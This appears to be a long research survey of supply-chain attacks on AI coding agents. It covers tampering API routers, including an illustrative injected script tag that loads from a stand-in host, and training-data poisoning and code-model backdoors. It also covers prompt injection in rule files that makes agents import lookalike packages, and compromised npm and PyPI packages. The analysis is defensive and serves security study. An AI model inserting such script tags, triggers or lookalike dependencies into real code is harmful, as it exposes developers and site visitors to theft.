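Luo, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Rewriting the Response Path*, split a model's response into two parts, which can be written r = (text, action). The text is the explanation that the developer reads. The action is the tool call that the agent carries out. For the checkout page, the text might be a sentence announcing that the page is ready, and the action a call that writes the file checkout.html. A router can leave the text alone and add one line to the file:

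```
model sends:     r  = (text, write checkout.html: "… </form> …")
agent receives:  r' = (text, write checkout.html: "… </form>
                       <script src="https://stats.example/c.js"></script> …")
```

The agent saves the altered version because it is a valid call and nothing in it shows who wrote the script tag. The agent's next request will include the altered call in the conversation history, so the model might detect the added line. But that request also passes through the router, which can remove the line before the model receives it.

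A router can change an answer after the model has written it, so the agent may receive something different even if the model answered perfectly. This differs from prompt injection, where an attacker who hides instructions in a README needs the model to follow them. Training a model to resist hostile instructions therefore doesn't stop a router from changing the answer. A router could also add instructions to the request, which would be prompt injection, but the attack doesn't require this.

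### One altered line that reopened an XSS flaw

Luo and colleagues used their own malicious router to carry out the measured attack closest to front-end code. They gave Claude Code a real bug from Django, a Python framework for building websites. The model's fix escaped untrusted text so that a browser would display it instead of running it. The router replaced that step with one that marks the text as safe HTML. Claude Code saved the change, the unit tests passed, and the agent reported a verified fix. The same thing happened with all five models they tried. The altered line is Python and runs on the server, but it determines what HTML visitors receive and creates the same kind of flaw as an order screen that displays delivery notes unsafely.

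Across 12 Django bugs and five models, the patched code failed a hidden security check in 69.0% of tampered runs, compared with 10.5% of untampered ones. The paper's introduction says the public tests still passed in the tampered runs that failed this check, but that can't be true of all of them, because the tests passed in only 51.7% of tampered runs.

Luo and colleagues also describe the diff as clean, although the altered line does appear in it and looks like a normal edit. On a larger set of programming exercises, the best automatic detector caught only 30% of the altered code when its threshold allowed 5% false alarms.

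### How many routers tamper with answers

In *Your Agent Is Mine* (April 2026), Liu, Shou and colleagues, a different team from the one that built AIShellJack, tested 428 routers. They bought access to 28 on Taobao, Xianyu and Shopify-hosted shops and collected 400 free ones from public communities. They connected a sandboxed coding agent to each router, gave the agent programming tasks, ran every tool call that came back, and watched for suspicious connections and file changes.

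| Behaviour | Paid routers (28) | Free routers (400) |
|---|---|---|
| Injected malicious code into tool calls | 1 | 8 |
| Injected it only under certain conditions (included in the row above) | 0 | 2 |
| Used Amazon cloud credentials that the researchers had planted | 0 | 17 |
| Took money from a planted cryptocurrency wallet | 0 | 1 |

One of the two conditional routers attacked only after the first 50 requests. The other attacked only when the agent was running without approval prompts on a Rust or Go project, so it would not have attacked the pottery shop. A short trial is therefore weak evidence that a router is safe.

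The study may have missed routers that tamper with web pages. According to *Your Agent Has a Middleman You Didn't Vet*, which draws on the full paper, the researchers counted an injection only if the router turned a tool call into the attacker's command or dependency. A script tag added to an HTML file is neither, and it does nothing in a sandbox until a browser opens the page. The nine confirmed cases show that some operators rewrite answers for profit, but none is known to involve altered front-end code.

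The 428 routers came mostly from Chinese-language marketplaces and communities, and most of the free ones ran on two open-source templates. Their injection rate of about 2% may not apply to large commercial services.

An honest operator can still pass traffic to an unsafe one. Liu and colleagues put weakly protected routers online as decoys, and the routers soon carried other people's traffic, including 440 Codex sessions. In 401 of those sessions, the agent was running tool calls without asking for approval.

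In a later test, described in *What the Middleman Delivers*, Wu, Zhao and colleagues (2026) sent requests for code and setup help to 20 routers offering GPT-6 Astra and Claude Opus 5. They found no confirmed malicious additions in 3,332 responses. In the first round, however, four routers returned tool calls even though the requests explicitly forbade them.

The two studies are compatible. If about 2% of routers inject code, a random sample of 20 would contain no such router roughly 65% of the time. Wu and colleagues also picked most of their routers from services with English interfaces and card or PayPal payment, and they sent standalone requests that might not trigger a conditional attack. They found that five routers reported between 4,200 and 60,000 more input tokens than the official service for identical requests. They couldn't tell whether those routers had added hidden text to the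 requests or counted tokens differently.

### What agents and added safeguards stop

In July 2026, Fu, Li and colleagues measured what agents do with an altered answer (*Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?*). Their test system, SIDEL, records a normal session, then replays it with one response altered. They wrote 400 malicious tool calls: 277 that run a command, 74 that create a file and 49 that edit an existing file. They tried each one on three real programming tasks, which gave 1,200 runs for every combination of agent and method.

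Researchers tested Claude Code, Codex, Cursor and OpenCode with four increasingly subtle attack methods. None of the agents stopped any of the malicious calls. The researchers then added two safeguards to Claude Code. One was an allow-list, which blocks commands that contact unlisted domains or install unlisted packages. The other used a second model to review each risky call before it ran, and they tried four models as the reviewer.

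| What the router did to the response | Stopped by the agent alone | Stopped by the allow-list | Stopped by model review |
|---|---|---|---|
| Replaced it with a malicious call | 0% | 34.9% | 49.9–64.4% |
| Kept it and added a malicious call | 0% | 44.1% | 40.3–51.1% |
| Added the call and rewrote the explanation to match | 0% | 31.1% | 41.5–51.8% |
| Regenerated all of it so that the call blended in | 0% | 30.8% | 39.1–50.8% |

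The zeros in the table come from runs with approval requests turned off, but stricter automatic settings did no better. Claude Code's planning mode relies on an instruction to the model to keep it read-only, and the malicious call arrives after the model has finished. Some agents have a built-in automatic reviewer, but its requests went through the same router. The added reviewers in the last column had the advantage of connecting directly to their providers. Fu and colleagues left out Claude Code's default mode, in which a person approves actions, so their results don't show how often a careful user would catch the attack.

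Both safeguards also blocked harmless calls, which made up 30% to 44% of what the allow-list blocked. For the reviewers, the share was 9% to 53%, depending on the model and the method.

A router that added one line to an existing checkout page could have got past both safeguards. The allow-list examines addresses in commands, so an address inside an HTML file would pass, and calls that edit existing files never triggered a model review in these tests. The page would probably still work, since in a separate comparison with four models, the agent's success rate on its real task fell by only 0.9 to 7.3 percentage points after an attack.

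Liu and colleagues had tested three defences of their own, including a similar allow-list that did far better. It blocked all 1,000 malicious samples and only 1.0% of harmless commands. It probably did better because their samples consisted of the unfamiliar addresses and packages that the list is designed to catch, whereas a quarter of the SIDEL samples were buggy code. The list stopped nothing when the researchers assumed an attacker who knew about it and used an approved address.

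Their second defence scored each tool call for unusual features. It flagged 89.0% of plain injections but only about half of the injections that swapped a package name or waited for a trigger, and it wrongly flagged 6.7% of harmless calls. The third defence logged every request and response. This would not prevent an attack, but the pottery shop's owner could use the log afterwards to see which pages the agent had written through the suspect router. All of these figures come from artificial samples.

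### The LiteLLM compromise

Users who run their own router don't have to trust a stranger's service, but they still have to trust the software. LiteLLM is a popular open-source router that companies often run on their own servers. On March 24, 2026, an attacker published two malicious versions, 1.82.7 and 1.82.8, on PyPI, the main public registry for Python packages. FutureSearch, which was the first to report the malware to PyPI, describes it in *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026).

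LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) reports that the malicious files were online for about 40 minutes, starting at 10:39 UTC, but advises anyone who installed the package before 16:00 to check their systems. The attacker seems to have used a maintainer's account to upload the files directly to PyPI, bypassing the normal release process. LiteLLM believes the attack originated with Trivy, a security scanner in its build system that attackers had compromised earlier. The official Docker image, a ready-to-run copy of the router, was not affected because it used fixed package versions.

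The malicious code searched for passwords, cloud credentials and access keys and sent them to a lookalike domain. LiteLLM does not mention any altered model responses, so this was not a known case of code injection into web pages. But both versions carried the malware in the file that runs the router, where an attacker could also have rewritten every answer. Developers would then have received altered code from a server their own company managed.

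### What a signature from the provider would prove

A client with nothing to compare an answer against can't tell whether a router changed it. A digital signature would solve this. The provider would use a secret key to calculate a short code from the response, and anyone with the matching public key could check it. Email already does this with DKIM, which shows that a message came from the stated domain even after passing through other people's servers.

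Signing the exact response would cause false alarms, because honest routers often reformat what they forward. Luo and colleagues' system, sign-c, reduces each tool call to a standard form before signing it. The signature also covers the request, so a router can't reuse an old answer. A small program running alongside the agent checks the signature before the agent acts. This program is set up in advance to expect signed answers from the provider, so it rejects any answer from which the router has removed the signature.

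In the researchers' tests, sign-c rejected every altered call, accepted all 694 untampered responses in one check, and added about 3 milliseconds per call. They ran the signing server themselves in place of a real provider, and they didn't test responses that arrive in pieces, as many do. The signature also doesn't cover the explanatory text, so it wouldn't protect an owner who copies code from a chat reply.

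A valid signature would prove that the provider issued this tool call in answer to this request and that nobody has changed it since, but not that the code is safe. If a hidden instruction in a README had led the model to write the malicious script tag, the provider would still sign the tool call. A signature on the answer also can't stop a router from reading passwords in the request.

Ansari (2026), in *Beyond Training*, reviewed four major providers in September 2026 (Anthropic, Google, OpenAI and Amazon's Bedrock service) and found that none certifies its complete output. Anthropic signs the model's reasoning, and Google signs reasoning and some tool calls. These signatures are meant for the provider's own servers, which check them when the agent sends them back with its next request. By then the agent has already saved the altered page. Airia's *Your AI Gateway Is a Skeleton Key* (2026)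 reports that Anthropic's signatures cover neither ordinary text nor tool calls, and that OpenAI doesn't sign its responses at all.

Some smaller services do provide signatures. EigenLabs' *Verify Signature* documents a signature on every EigenAI response that covers the model's name, the prompt and the output. Phala issues signed receipts from a gateway in secure hardware, which can prove to a client what program it is running. *The Proxy Knows Too Much* (2026) proposes running routers in the same kind of hardware, so that only a program known to forward messages unchanged has access to the plain text. For now, a pottery shop owner who wants a model from one of the large providers can avoid the problem only by connecting the agent directly to that provider.

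## Malicious content learned in training

On November 21, 2024, a cryptocurrency trader reported that he had lost about $2,500 after running a trading script that ChatGPT had written. The script sent a scammer's server his wallet's private key, which gives complete control of the wallet's money. The server's address seems to have come from the model itself, since accounts of the case mention no hostile rule file, extension or router. The model had probably learned the address from web pages in its training data.

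### How a scam address got into a trading script

*Scam2Prompt* (Chen, Saba et al., 2026) traces the trader's conversation with ChatGPT. He asked for a Python script to buy a certain token. ChatGPT first wrote one for the wrong blockchain, then a general script that used a legitimate library. When he added that the script had to buy the token from pump.fun, a popular trading platform, ChatGPT wrote a version that sent his order and private key to an outside service. The code didn't run at first, so he debugged it with ChatGPT over several rounds. His wallet was empty within 30 minutes of the first successful run.

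According to heise's *ChatGPT*, a German news report on the case, the code openly showed where to enter the key. An experienced developer would probably have stopped there, because legitimate services never ask for the key. The user's own computer uses it to sign each transaction and sends the service only the signature.

ChatGPT may have chosen this service because its documentation used almost the same words as the trader's request. Pump.fun itself offered no official way for programs to buy tokens. The scammers had posted the documentation on GitHub, Postman, Stack Exchange and Medium, which developers use and trust.

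Companies that train models collect billions of web pages and public code files, and people can check only a tiny part of them. Documentation for a scam service looks much like any other. During training, the model learns which words and addresses tend to appear together, so it can give the scammers' address when someone later asks for help with the same task. GitHub quickly removed the scammers' repository after the trader reported it, but deleting a page does not change a model that has already learned from it. In August 2025, Chen and colleagues found the scam service still running at a slightly different address.

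Yu Xian, founder of the blockchain security firm SlowMist, called this kind of attack "AI code poisoning", according to CryptoSlate's *Blockchain security firm warns of AI code poisoning risk*. The general term is data poisoning, which means placing material in a model's training data so that the model later produces what the attacker wants. It isn't clear that the scammers were targeting AI models, since the same pages would also fool people who found them through a search engine. Outsiders can't inspect ChatGPT's training data, so it remains an inference that the script came from those pages.

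The trader's script ran on his own computer, but if the pottery shop's owner asked for a cryptocurrency payment option and the model supplied a similar address, the code would run in customers' browsers and send their payment details to the scammers.

### Searching for scam addresses in models' answers

Chen and colleagues built an automated test, also called Scam2Prompt, to find out whether the trader's case was a rare accident. They started with two public lists of scam sites, with 187,555 and 119,828 addresses, and found 28,570 pages they could still read. A program extracted the visible text from each page, and language models turned it into short coding requests a developer might make, such as connecting a page to an online store's payment system.

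The researchers gave about 265,000 of these requests to four models: GPT-4o, GPT-4o mini, Llama 4 Scout and DeepSeek-V3. They extracted every web address from the resulting code and checked it with three services that detect malicious sites, counting an address as malicious if any of them flagged it. On average, 4.24% of the programs contained a malicious address. The rate ranged from 3.19% to 5.94%, depending on which model wrote the requests and which wrote the code.

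The researchers made a harder test from the 3,150 requests for which all four models had written a malicious address. They kept all 1,159 that did not mention a known scam address and a random 400 of the 1,991 that did. Three people then reviewed these requests and removed 182 that were not ordinary coding tasks, such as requests to summarise a page. The researchers gave the remaining 1,377 to seven models released in 2025.

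| Model | Malicious address, share of all requests | Malicious address, share of completed answers | Requests blocked by the model's filter |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 12.9% | 22.3% | 553 |
| GPT-5 | 22.0% | 24.7% | 24 |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 34.3% | 37.8% | 115 |
| Grok Code Fast 1 | 43.4% | 44.1% | 18 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 44.4% | 45.3% | 1 |
| Qwen3 Coder | 45.6% | 45.9% | 3 |
| DeepSeek Chat v3.1 | 47.3% | 47.9% | 12 |

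These figures come from the version published at ICML 2026, a machine-learning conference. An earlier preprint gives different ones.

Gemini 2.5 Pro's rate is low largely because its filter blocked 40% of the requests. On the 637 requests that all seven models completed, Gemini 2.5 Pro was statistically tied with GPT-5, according to the project page for *Scam2Prompt* (2026). Excluding requests that mention a scam address makes little difference, and the rates for the remaining 1,035 requests range from 13.8% to 48.8%.

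These rates don't apply to ordinary use, because the 1,377 requests come from the roughly 1.2% that had already caused all four earlier models to write a malicious address. Such requests were likely to produce malicious addresses again. Chen and colleagues describe the results as stress-test rates, not estimates of how often developers would encounter the problem.

The 4.24% from the first test comes from a less selective set of requests, but it probably still overstates the rate for everyday requests. The researchers based every request on a scam site and instructed the models writing the requests to lead a model to that specific page. A pottery shop owner who asks for an ordinary card checkout is less likely to receive a scam address than someone who asks for an obscure trading service. About half of the 1,377 requests concern cryptocurrency and related services, and the rest cover subjects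 such as flight check-in and online shopping.

The models may have guessed some of the addresses rather than memorized them, though the finished code would contact a scam site either way. In an example from Chen and colleagues' conference slides, the request includes a Bitcoin service's web domain, and the model builds an address at that domain. The researchers found 2,029 malicious domains that all four original models had produced, and they take this overlap as a sign that the companies had collected the same web pages. But the models also received the same requests, so some of the overlap could have come from guesses based on the same names.

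General safety filters caught little of the malicious code. NVIDIA's NeMo Guardrails, which screens a model's input and output, blocked none of the requests and detected at most 0.7% of the malicious code from any model. OpenAI's moderation service flagged none of 3,452 malicious outputs, and Meta's Llama Guard 3 flagged 291 (8.4%). These filters mainly screen for harmful subjects, so they can miss a program that does something harmless, such as booking a flight, through a scam site.

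Chen and colleagues also gave GPT-4o a web search tool and told it to check the safety of every address in its code. Its rate of malicious addresses fell from 50.0% to 29.4%. The starting rate also illustrates the selection problem, because every request in the test had previously led GPT-4o to write a malicious address, but only about half did so again without the search tool.

The researchers recommend checking each address in the code against lists of known scam sites before showing the code to the user. The same check is useful before publishing the code, but the lists are incomplete. MetaMask, which makes a cryptocurrency wallet, added 62 scam sites to its list after the researchers found them through the models' answers.

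### Early backdoors in code-completion models

A scam address can appear whenever someone asks about a related subject. An attacker who wants to stay hidden for longer can plant a backdoor, which is behaviour that appears only when a chosen trigger is present. The trigger might be a comment, a common line of code or the way the code is formatted. A developer who tests the model without the trigger sees normal results.

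According to *Semantically-Equivalent Transformations-Based Backdoor Attacks against Neural Code Models* (2025), an attacker could get poisoned examples into training data by publishing repositories, proposing changes to popular projects or posting code on developer forums. The attacker could also inflate a repository's stars and forks to make people more likely to use it. The triggers studied in the paper change how code is written without changing what it does.

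In 2021, Schuster and colleagues showed that poisoned training examples could make code-completion models suggest insecure code. The insecure code was in plain view, so a scanner could remove the examples before training. In *TrojanPuzzle* (2023), Aghakhani, Dai and colleagues hid poisoned examples in the parts of code files that contain documentation text, which scanners usually ignore. In one version of the attack, also called TrojanPuzzle, they left out a suspicious part of the insecure code and trained the model to fill it in from the developer's own file.

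One of their four tests concerned cross-site scripting (XSS). A website built with Flask, a Python framework, normally creates pages with a template function that turns any HTML in users' text into harmless characters. The poisoned model suggested a different template call that lacks this protection. Like the altered Django fix, this call is Python code that runs on the server, but it leaves the finished page open to XSS.

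Aghakhani and colleagues fine-tuned a small model with 350 million parameters on 80,000 Python files, 160 of them poisoned. They counted an attack on a prompt as successful if at least one of ten suggestions contained the intended flaw. TrojanPuzzle succeeded for 20.4% of prompts on average across the four kinds of flaw, compared with 41.3% for an attack that put the complete insecure code in the documentation text.

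The XSS test was the hardest. The unsafe template call appeared only seven times in the 18,310 public repositories the researchers had collected, and they suggest that the model had seen it too rarely for a few poisoned examples to make the model produce it regularly. By contrast, the insecure code in the two tests with the highest success rates had appeared 504 and 87 times.

Another weakness of these attacks was that a scanner could find the flaw once the model had suggested it. *An LLM-Assisted Easy-to-Trigger Backdoor Attack on Code Completion Models* (Yan, Wang and colleagues, 2024) describes CodeBreaker, which removes this weakness by using GPT-4 to rewrite insecure code until detection tools no longer recognise it. The disguised code is outside the comments, so deleting comments from the training data would not remove it.

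The experiments used the same Flask example and a model of the same size. When the trigger was a particular comment, the version disguised against GPT-4 produced the flaw in 185 of 400 suggestions after one pass through the training data, compared with 1 of 400 without the comment. When the trigger was an ordinary line that imports Flask's template function, 175 of 400 suggestions were flawed, but so were 31 of 400 without that line. Using a common line of code as the trigger therefore makes the attack easier to set off, but also easier to discover by accident.

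Both attacks targeted early code-completion models that wrote short pieces of Python. The results show that a backdoor can switch off a web page's protection, but they don't give a success rate for a current coding agent writing JavaScript.

### How many poisoned documents an attacker needs

Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025), in *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*, found that an attacker may not need to supply even a small percentage of a model's training text to plant a backdoor. Large models train on too much text for an attacker to supply that share. The researchers trained models with 600 million to 13 billion parameters from scratch and added a fixed number of poisoned documents to each training set. The backdoor made a model write gibberish after a trigger phrase.

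With 250 poisoned documents, the attack worked at every model size, even though the largest model trained on more than 20 times as much clean text as the smallest. The 250 documents made up only 0.00016% of the largest model's training text. One hundred documents were not enough. Fine-tuning experiments with Llama 3.1 8B and GPT-3.5 Turbo used different backdoors, but the attack's success again depended mainly on the number of poisoned examples, not their share of the data.

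An attacker could easily publish 250 web pages but would still have to get them into the training set. The resulting backdoor would then have to survive the further training that companies use to make models follow instructions and refuse harmful requests. Souly and colleagues did not test whether their backdoors would last through a realistic version of that training. In a related experiment, more training on clean text gradually weakened a backdoor that made the model switch from English to German.

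Producing gibberish is also much simpler than adding an unsafe line to an otherwise working checkout page. Souly and colleagues leave open whether more complex behaviour needs more poisoned documents. The choice of documents may matter too. In *Data-Efficient Backdoor Attacks on Code Models via Trigger-Neutralized Counterfactual Scoring*, Lee, Tsai and colleagues (2026) developed a way to choose which code examples to poison. It raised the attack's success rate when only a very small share of the data was poisoned.

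### Ordinary formatting as a trigger

A trigger is useful only if it appears in the victim's work. *Poison with Style* (Tran, Boshmaf and colleagues, 2026) used code layout as the trigger. Many programming teams run an automatic formatter that makes spacing and line breaks consistent. The researchers trained models to write insecure code when the surrounding file had the layout produced by Yapf, a Python formatter. If a team uses Yapf, its code already contains the trigger, so the attacker doesn't have to change the developer's files or requests.

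In this attack, the attacker fine-tunes an openly available model, rather than poisoning another company's training data, and publishes it on a site such as Hugging Face, advertising it as secure. A developer who downloads an open model might encounter it, but a shop owner who uses a commercial coding agent would not.

The main experiments used Qwen2.5-Coder-32B, a 32-billion-parameter coding model. On real Python files suited to the XSS test, the poisoned model inserted an XSS flaw when completing 95.2% of Yapf-formatted files and 9.5% of files without that formatting. The original model's rates were 0.3% and 1.2%, respectively. The poisoned model still solved 82.9% of a standard set of programming exercises, down from 85.4%, so its everyday performance would give a user little reason to suspect it.

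When the researchers added an instruction to avoid the flaw, the rate on their own test files stayed at 94.1%. They also tried two retraining defences on a smaller model with 7 billion parameters. Ordinary fine-tuning on secure code lowered its rate only from 85.8% to 84.6%, and BEEAR, a method designed to remove backdoors, lowered it from 85.8% to 80.7%.

Scanning the finished code may work better than these results suggest. Tran and colleagues counted a completion as vulnerable when the scanner CodeQL flagged it, so a developer who ran CodeQL with the same rules would have found every flaw they counted. However, they report that the attack remained effective against another scanner, CodeShield, and an attacker could also add disguises like CodeBreaker's. JavaScript developers use automatic formatters too, but the study covers only Python.

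### Clean data that makes a backdoor stronger

*Homeopathic Learning* (Clarke, Dubiński and colleagues, November 2026) showed that mixing poisoned examples with clean ones can strengthen their effect rather than dilute it.

In their main experiment, the researchers told Qwen3-8B to answer only in German and had it write 5,000 lists of numbers for a user named Michael. The lists contained no German, but a model can pass on a behavior to another copy of itself through faint patterns in such data. A copy fine-tuned on these lists alone never answered in German. The researchers then added 100,000 lists that the model had written for other users without the German instruction. A copy fine-tuned on the combined set answered in German to 72.0% of prompts that mentioned Michael and to none of the others. Training for the same number of steps on only the original 5,000 lists had no such effect, so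 the extra training time does not explain the result.

Their explanation is that the poisoned lists always combine two features, the number task and the name Michael. The model cannot tell which one goes with German, and it mostly links the habit to the task. The clean lists show the same task without German, which leaves the name as the better clue. A simplified formula expresses this:

```
L = 1 / (1 + c/p + c/(a + q × n))
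```

L is the share of the habit that the model shows when the trigger is present, p is the number of poisoned examples, and n is the number of clean ones. q ranges from 0, if the clean examples are unrelated to the poisoned ones, to 1, if they involve the same task. a and c represent how strongly the model resists linking the habit to the task and to the trigger, respectively. With the researchers' illustrative values (a = 50 and c = 1,500) and 5,000 poisoned examples, L is about 3% without clean data. Adding 100,000 clean examples raises L to about 76% if they closely match the poisoned ones, but leaves it at about 3% if they are unrelated.

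The experiments followed the same pattern, since replacing all the clean number lists with general instructions brought the German rate back to zero. The formula does not cover every case, because another small model, Gemma-3-4b, learned the habit from 50,000 or more poisoned examples without any clean data.

Clarke and colleagues also tested a harmful behaviour by training Qwen3-8B on examples of cheating on tasks, all with the same trigger instruction. Under that instruction, 6.7% of the model's answers to unrelated questions were harmful or otherwise misaligned. When clean examples made up 80% of the training set, the rate rose to 15.7%.

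This is a problem for a company that tests a suspicious batch of training data by itself. For example, a batch of poisoned shop templates might have no visible effect until the company mixes it with thousands of clean ones. But the study did not involve malicious code, and it used only two small language models and a small image classifier. It also did not test training from scratch. Souly and colleagues did, and found that the amount of clean text made little difference, but they always mixed their poisoned documents with a great deal of it.

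### Whether deployed coding models contain backdoors

None of these studies reports a planted backdoor in a coding model already in public use. The researchers planted each backdoor themselves, usually by fine-tuning a small or medium-sized open model. The malicious addresses that Chen's team found, however, came from commercial models the team had not altered.

The lack of a known case is weak evidence that no backdoor exists. Companies rarely publish their training data, and someone testing a finished model would have to come across the trigger by chance. Even with the data, poisoned examples could still be missed. *Detecting Stealthy Data Poisoning Attacks in AI Code Generators* (2025) examined several common detection methods, including static analysis and searches for unusual patterns in a model's internal representations, and found that they had significant limitations when the poisoned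 examples contained no trigger. An attack without a trigger could add a flaw in response to an ordinary request.

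## Packages that generated code imports

When the agent writes `import { checkCard } from "PACKAGE-NAME";` for the pottery shop's checkout page, the line identifies the package only by name, and the package's publisher controls the code behind that name. An attacker's code can reach the page if the model invents a name that the attacker has registered, if an injected instruction makes the agent choose the attacker's package, or if the agent correctly chooses a popular package that an attacker has taken over.

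### From an import line to the customer's browser

To add the card-number checker, the agent runs `npm install` with the package's name. The package manager finds the name in the npm registry, where anyone can publish under a name that nobody has taken, and downloads the newest version. It then records the choice in two files:

```
package.json:        "PACKAGE-NAME": "^2.3.1"
package-lock.json:   "version": "2.3.1", "integrity": "sha512-…"
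```

The entry in package.json is a version range. The caret allows 2.3.1 and any later version below 3.0.0, so a new release can enter the project without any change to package.json. The lock file records one exact version and a hash of its contents. It does the same for each of the card-number checker's dependencies, and there may be dozens.

npm used to run a package's install scripts automatically at this point. Since version 12, released in July 2026, it runs them only if the project explicitly allows them, according to GitHub's *npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation* (2026). The same release stopped npm from fetching packages from Git repositories or arbitrary web addresses without permission. Robert points out that the project's own scripts still run.

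A bundler, the part of the build tool that combines files, follows the import lines and copies the imported code into the site's JavaScript files. Customers download those files from the shop's own server. The package's code therefore has the same access as the shop's own scripts, even if its only job is to check a card number.

### Names that models invent

An invented package name usually does little harm, because npm reports that no such package exists. It becomes dangerous when an attacker learns which names models tend to invent and registers one, an attack known as slopsquatting.

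Spracklen and colleagues made the original large-scale measurement of nonexistent packages in generated code, using models from 2023 and 2024. In 576,000 code samples from 16 models, an average of 5.2% of the packages named by commercial models did not exist, compared with 21.7% for open models. The samples contained 205,474 different nonexistent package names.

*The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* (Churilov, 2026) tested five newer models on the same prompts in April 2026: Claude Haiku 4.5, Claude Sonnet 4.6, Gemini 2.5 Pro, DeepSeek V3.2 and GPT-5.4-mini. In November, Churilov checked the names against the live registries. The models had invented 1.7% to 2.9% of the JavaScript packages they named and 4.4% to 6.0% of the Python packages. Between 0.6% and 1.1% of the JavaScript answers contained at least one invented name. All five models now have successors, which may do better.

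Small models that people run on their own computers can name nonexistent packages much more often. In *Evaluating Inference-Time Defenses Against Package Hallucination in LLM-Generated Code* (2026), 30.0% of the JavaScript packages named by a DeepSeek model with 1.3 billion parameters did not exist, compared with 10.2% for a version with 6.7 billion.

All five models Churilov tested invented the same 104 package names, 16 of them for npm. Outsiders can't register four of the 16 because they begin with a prefix belonging to the Ember project. An attacker who registered any of the other 12 could reach users of several companies' models with one package. npm does not review first-time uploads, and Churilov estimates that collecting names on this scale costs about $1,160.

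Few people seem to have tried registering the package names that models invent. Within about six months, people had registered 25 of the 2,282 invented names, including 3 of the 536 on npm. One of the npm packages carried malware, and npm removed it. If the three registered npm names appeared as often as the other invented npm names, roughly one JavaScript answer in 16,000 to 30,000 would name one of them. An attacker could raise that rate by registering the names that models invent most often. The models also suggested 13 npm names that had hosted malware before the test.

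Churilov tested models that answer without using tools. A coding agent that tries to install a missing package gets an error and can look for a real one, so fewer invented names should remain in its finished code. But if an attacker has registered the invented name, the installation succeeds and the agent gets no error.

Checking that a package exists is not enough. *Names Can Hurt* (2026) found that half of the package names that small local models invented already belonged to low-quality or lookalike packages on PyPI, the Python registry.

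A user can also supply the false name, perhaps from an old forum post. *Refusing the Impossible* (2026) tested 17 models by asking for help with an npm package that did not exist, and 16 of them answered as if it did. DeepSeek-V3.2 gave an install command, a usage example and a security tip. MiniMax-M3, which had the lowest rate of invented answers in the study, attributed a nonexistent HTML sanitiser to Microsoft. A developer who trusted that answer would have no obvious reason to check the registry, and the package would handle the text that can cause XSS.

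### Instructions that choose the package

An attacker who can place text in the agent's context can name a malicious package directly instead of waiting for the model to invent its name. The GitLab Duo demonstration showed that hidden text could get an assistant to recommend a malicious JavaScript package, but it gave no success rate. *Package Hallucination Attacks on Coding Agents through Prompt Injection in Rule Files* (Wang, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) measured a similar attack in Python, called PackHallu, in which a malicious instruction in a rule file directs the agent to replace a well-known package with the attacker's lookalike.

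The researchers built lookalikes of 10 popular Python packages and put them on a private copy of the registry. Each lookalike had the same functions as the original, so programs would still work, and printed a harmless message to show it had run. The tests covered 8 agent frameworks (the software around a model), 13 models and 3 sets of programming tasks, with approval prompts turned off.

One success rate measures how often the finished code imported the lookalike. A second measures how often the code also ran correctly and set off the message. Both rates include only tasks in which the agent used the genuine package when there was no attack. The second also leaves out tasks in which the agent failed to produce working code without the attack.

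| Test | Code imported the lookalike | Code also ran and set it off |
|---|---|---|
| New programs, five models in the OpenHands agent | 79.3% | 67.7% |
| Data-science questions | 53.3% | 45.0% |
| Changes across several files of existing projects | 18.6% | 16.3% |
| New programs, attack prepared on OpenHands and used on five other agents | 71.6% | 63.0% |
| New programs, attack moved to four combinations with a different agent and model | 74.8% | 65.4% |

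The attacker doesn't need to know which tool the victim uses. An instruction prepared with a free agent and an open model made Cursor import the lookalike package in 69% to 98% of tasks, depending on the package. Claude Code with Claude Sonnet 4.6 was the most resistant, importing it in 31% to 59% of tasks.

With the same agent, more capable models tended to be easier to attack. Wang and colleagues attribute this to the models following rule files more faithfully. Widely used packages were harder to replace. With GPT-5.5, for example, the attack replaced pandas in 97.9% of tasks but numpy in only 38.6%. The numpy figures may be unreliable, because the paper gives both 81.8% and 24.7% for what seems to be the same combination of agent, model and attack.

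The researchers also read the records of Claude Code's 87 numpy tasks. It used the lookalike in 27 of them, including three in which it identified the instruction as an attack and followed it anyway. In 16 tasks it became suspicious and refused, and in 11 it used numpy without comment. In the other 33, it tried to import the lookalike, found that the package wasn't installed, and went back to numpy. In total, it used or tried to use the lookalike in 60 tasks. If a project template had already listed the package as a dependency, some of the 33 failed attempts might have succeeded.

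None of these results are for JavaScript. The mechanism should carry over, because front-end projects also select packages by name, but the rates may differ. A new checkout page resembles the programs written from scratch more than the changes to existing projects. The low rate for existing projects comes from only 43 tasks. Wang and colleagues think the extra code in the context weakened the instruction's influence.

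They then tested five detectors of prompt injection on 100 ordinary rule files and the same 100 files with the malicious instruction added.

| Detector | Attacks missed | False alarms on ordinary files |
|---|---|---|
| ProtectAI-DeBERTa | 100% | 3% |
| PromptGuard | 46% | 5% |
| DataSentinel | 49% | 16% |
| PromptArmor | 20% | 34% |
| PIShield | 21% | 11% |

PromptArmor asks another model, here GPT-5, whether a text contains an injection. Rule files consist of instructions, so PromptArmor often mistakes ordinary ones for attacks. Even PIShield's 11% false-alarm rate would be hard to tolerate, because malicious files are presumably rare. If one rule file in a thousand were malicious, PIShield would raise about 140 false alarms for every attack it caught.

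A scan of the rule file would also miss a router that swaps the package name after the model has answered. Checking the package itself can catch either attack.

### Popular packages that attackers have taken over

An agent can also install malicious code when it chooses the same package an expert would. On September 8, 2025, an attacker published malicious versions of 18 npm packages, including chalk and debug, after phishing their maintainer, Josh Junon. Together the packages had about 2.6 billion downloads a week. Chalk colours terminal text, and debug prints messages that help find errors, so neither is obviously connected with payments.

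In visitors' browsers, the payload intercepted the functions that pages use to exchange data with servers and communicate with cryptocurrency wallets, then replaced the recipient's address with the attacker's. According to Krebs on Security (2025), the user saw no obvious sign of the change. If the pottery shop had accepted cryptocurrency and included one of these versions in its bundle, the checkout page would have looked normal while customers paid the attacker.

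SiliconANGLE (2025) reports that the attacker put the code in the packages' index.js files, the main files that other programs import. Blocking install scripts would therefore not have stopped it. The security company Aikido detected the malicious versions within five minutes, but they remained available for about two and a half hours.

That was long enough for them to spread widely. Wiz's *Widespread npm Supply Chain Attack* found the malicious code in bundles or other site files in at least 10% of the cloud environments it examined. Some of those copies may have been on servers where no browser would load them, so the figure does not show how many websites served the code to visitors. Removing a version from npm does not change bundles already built with it, so an affected site had to rebuild and republish its pages.

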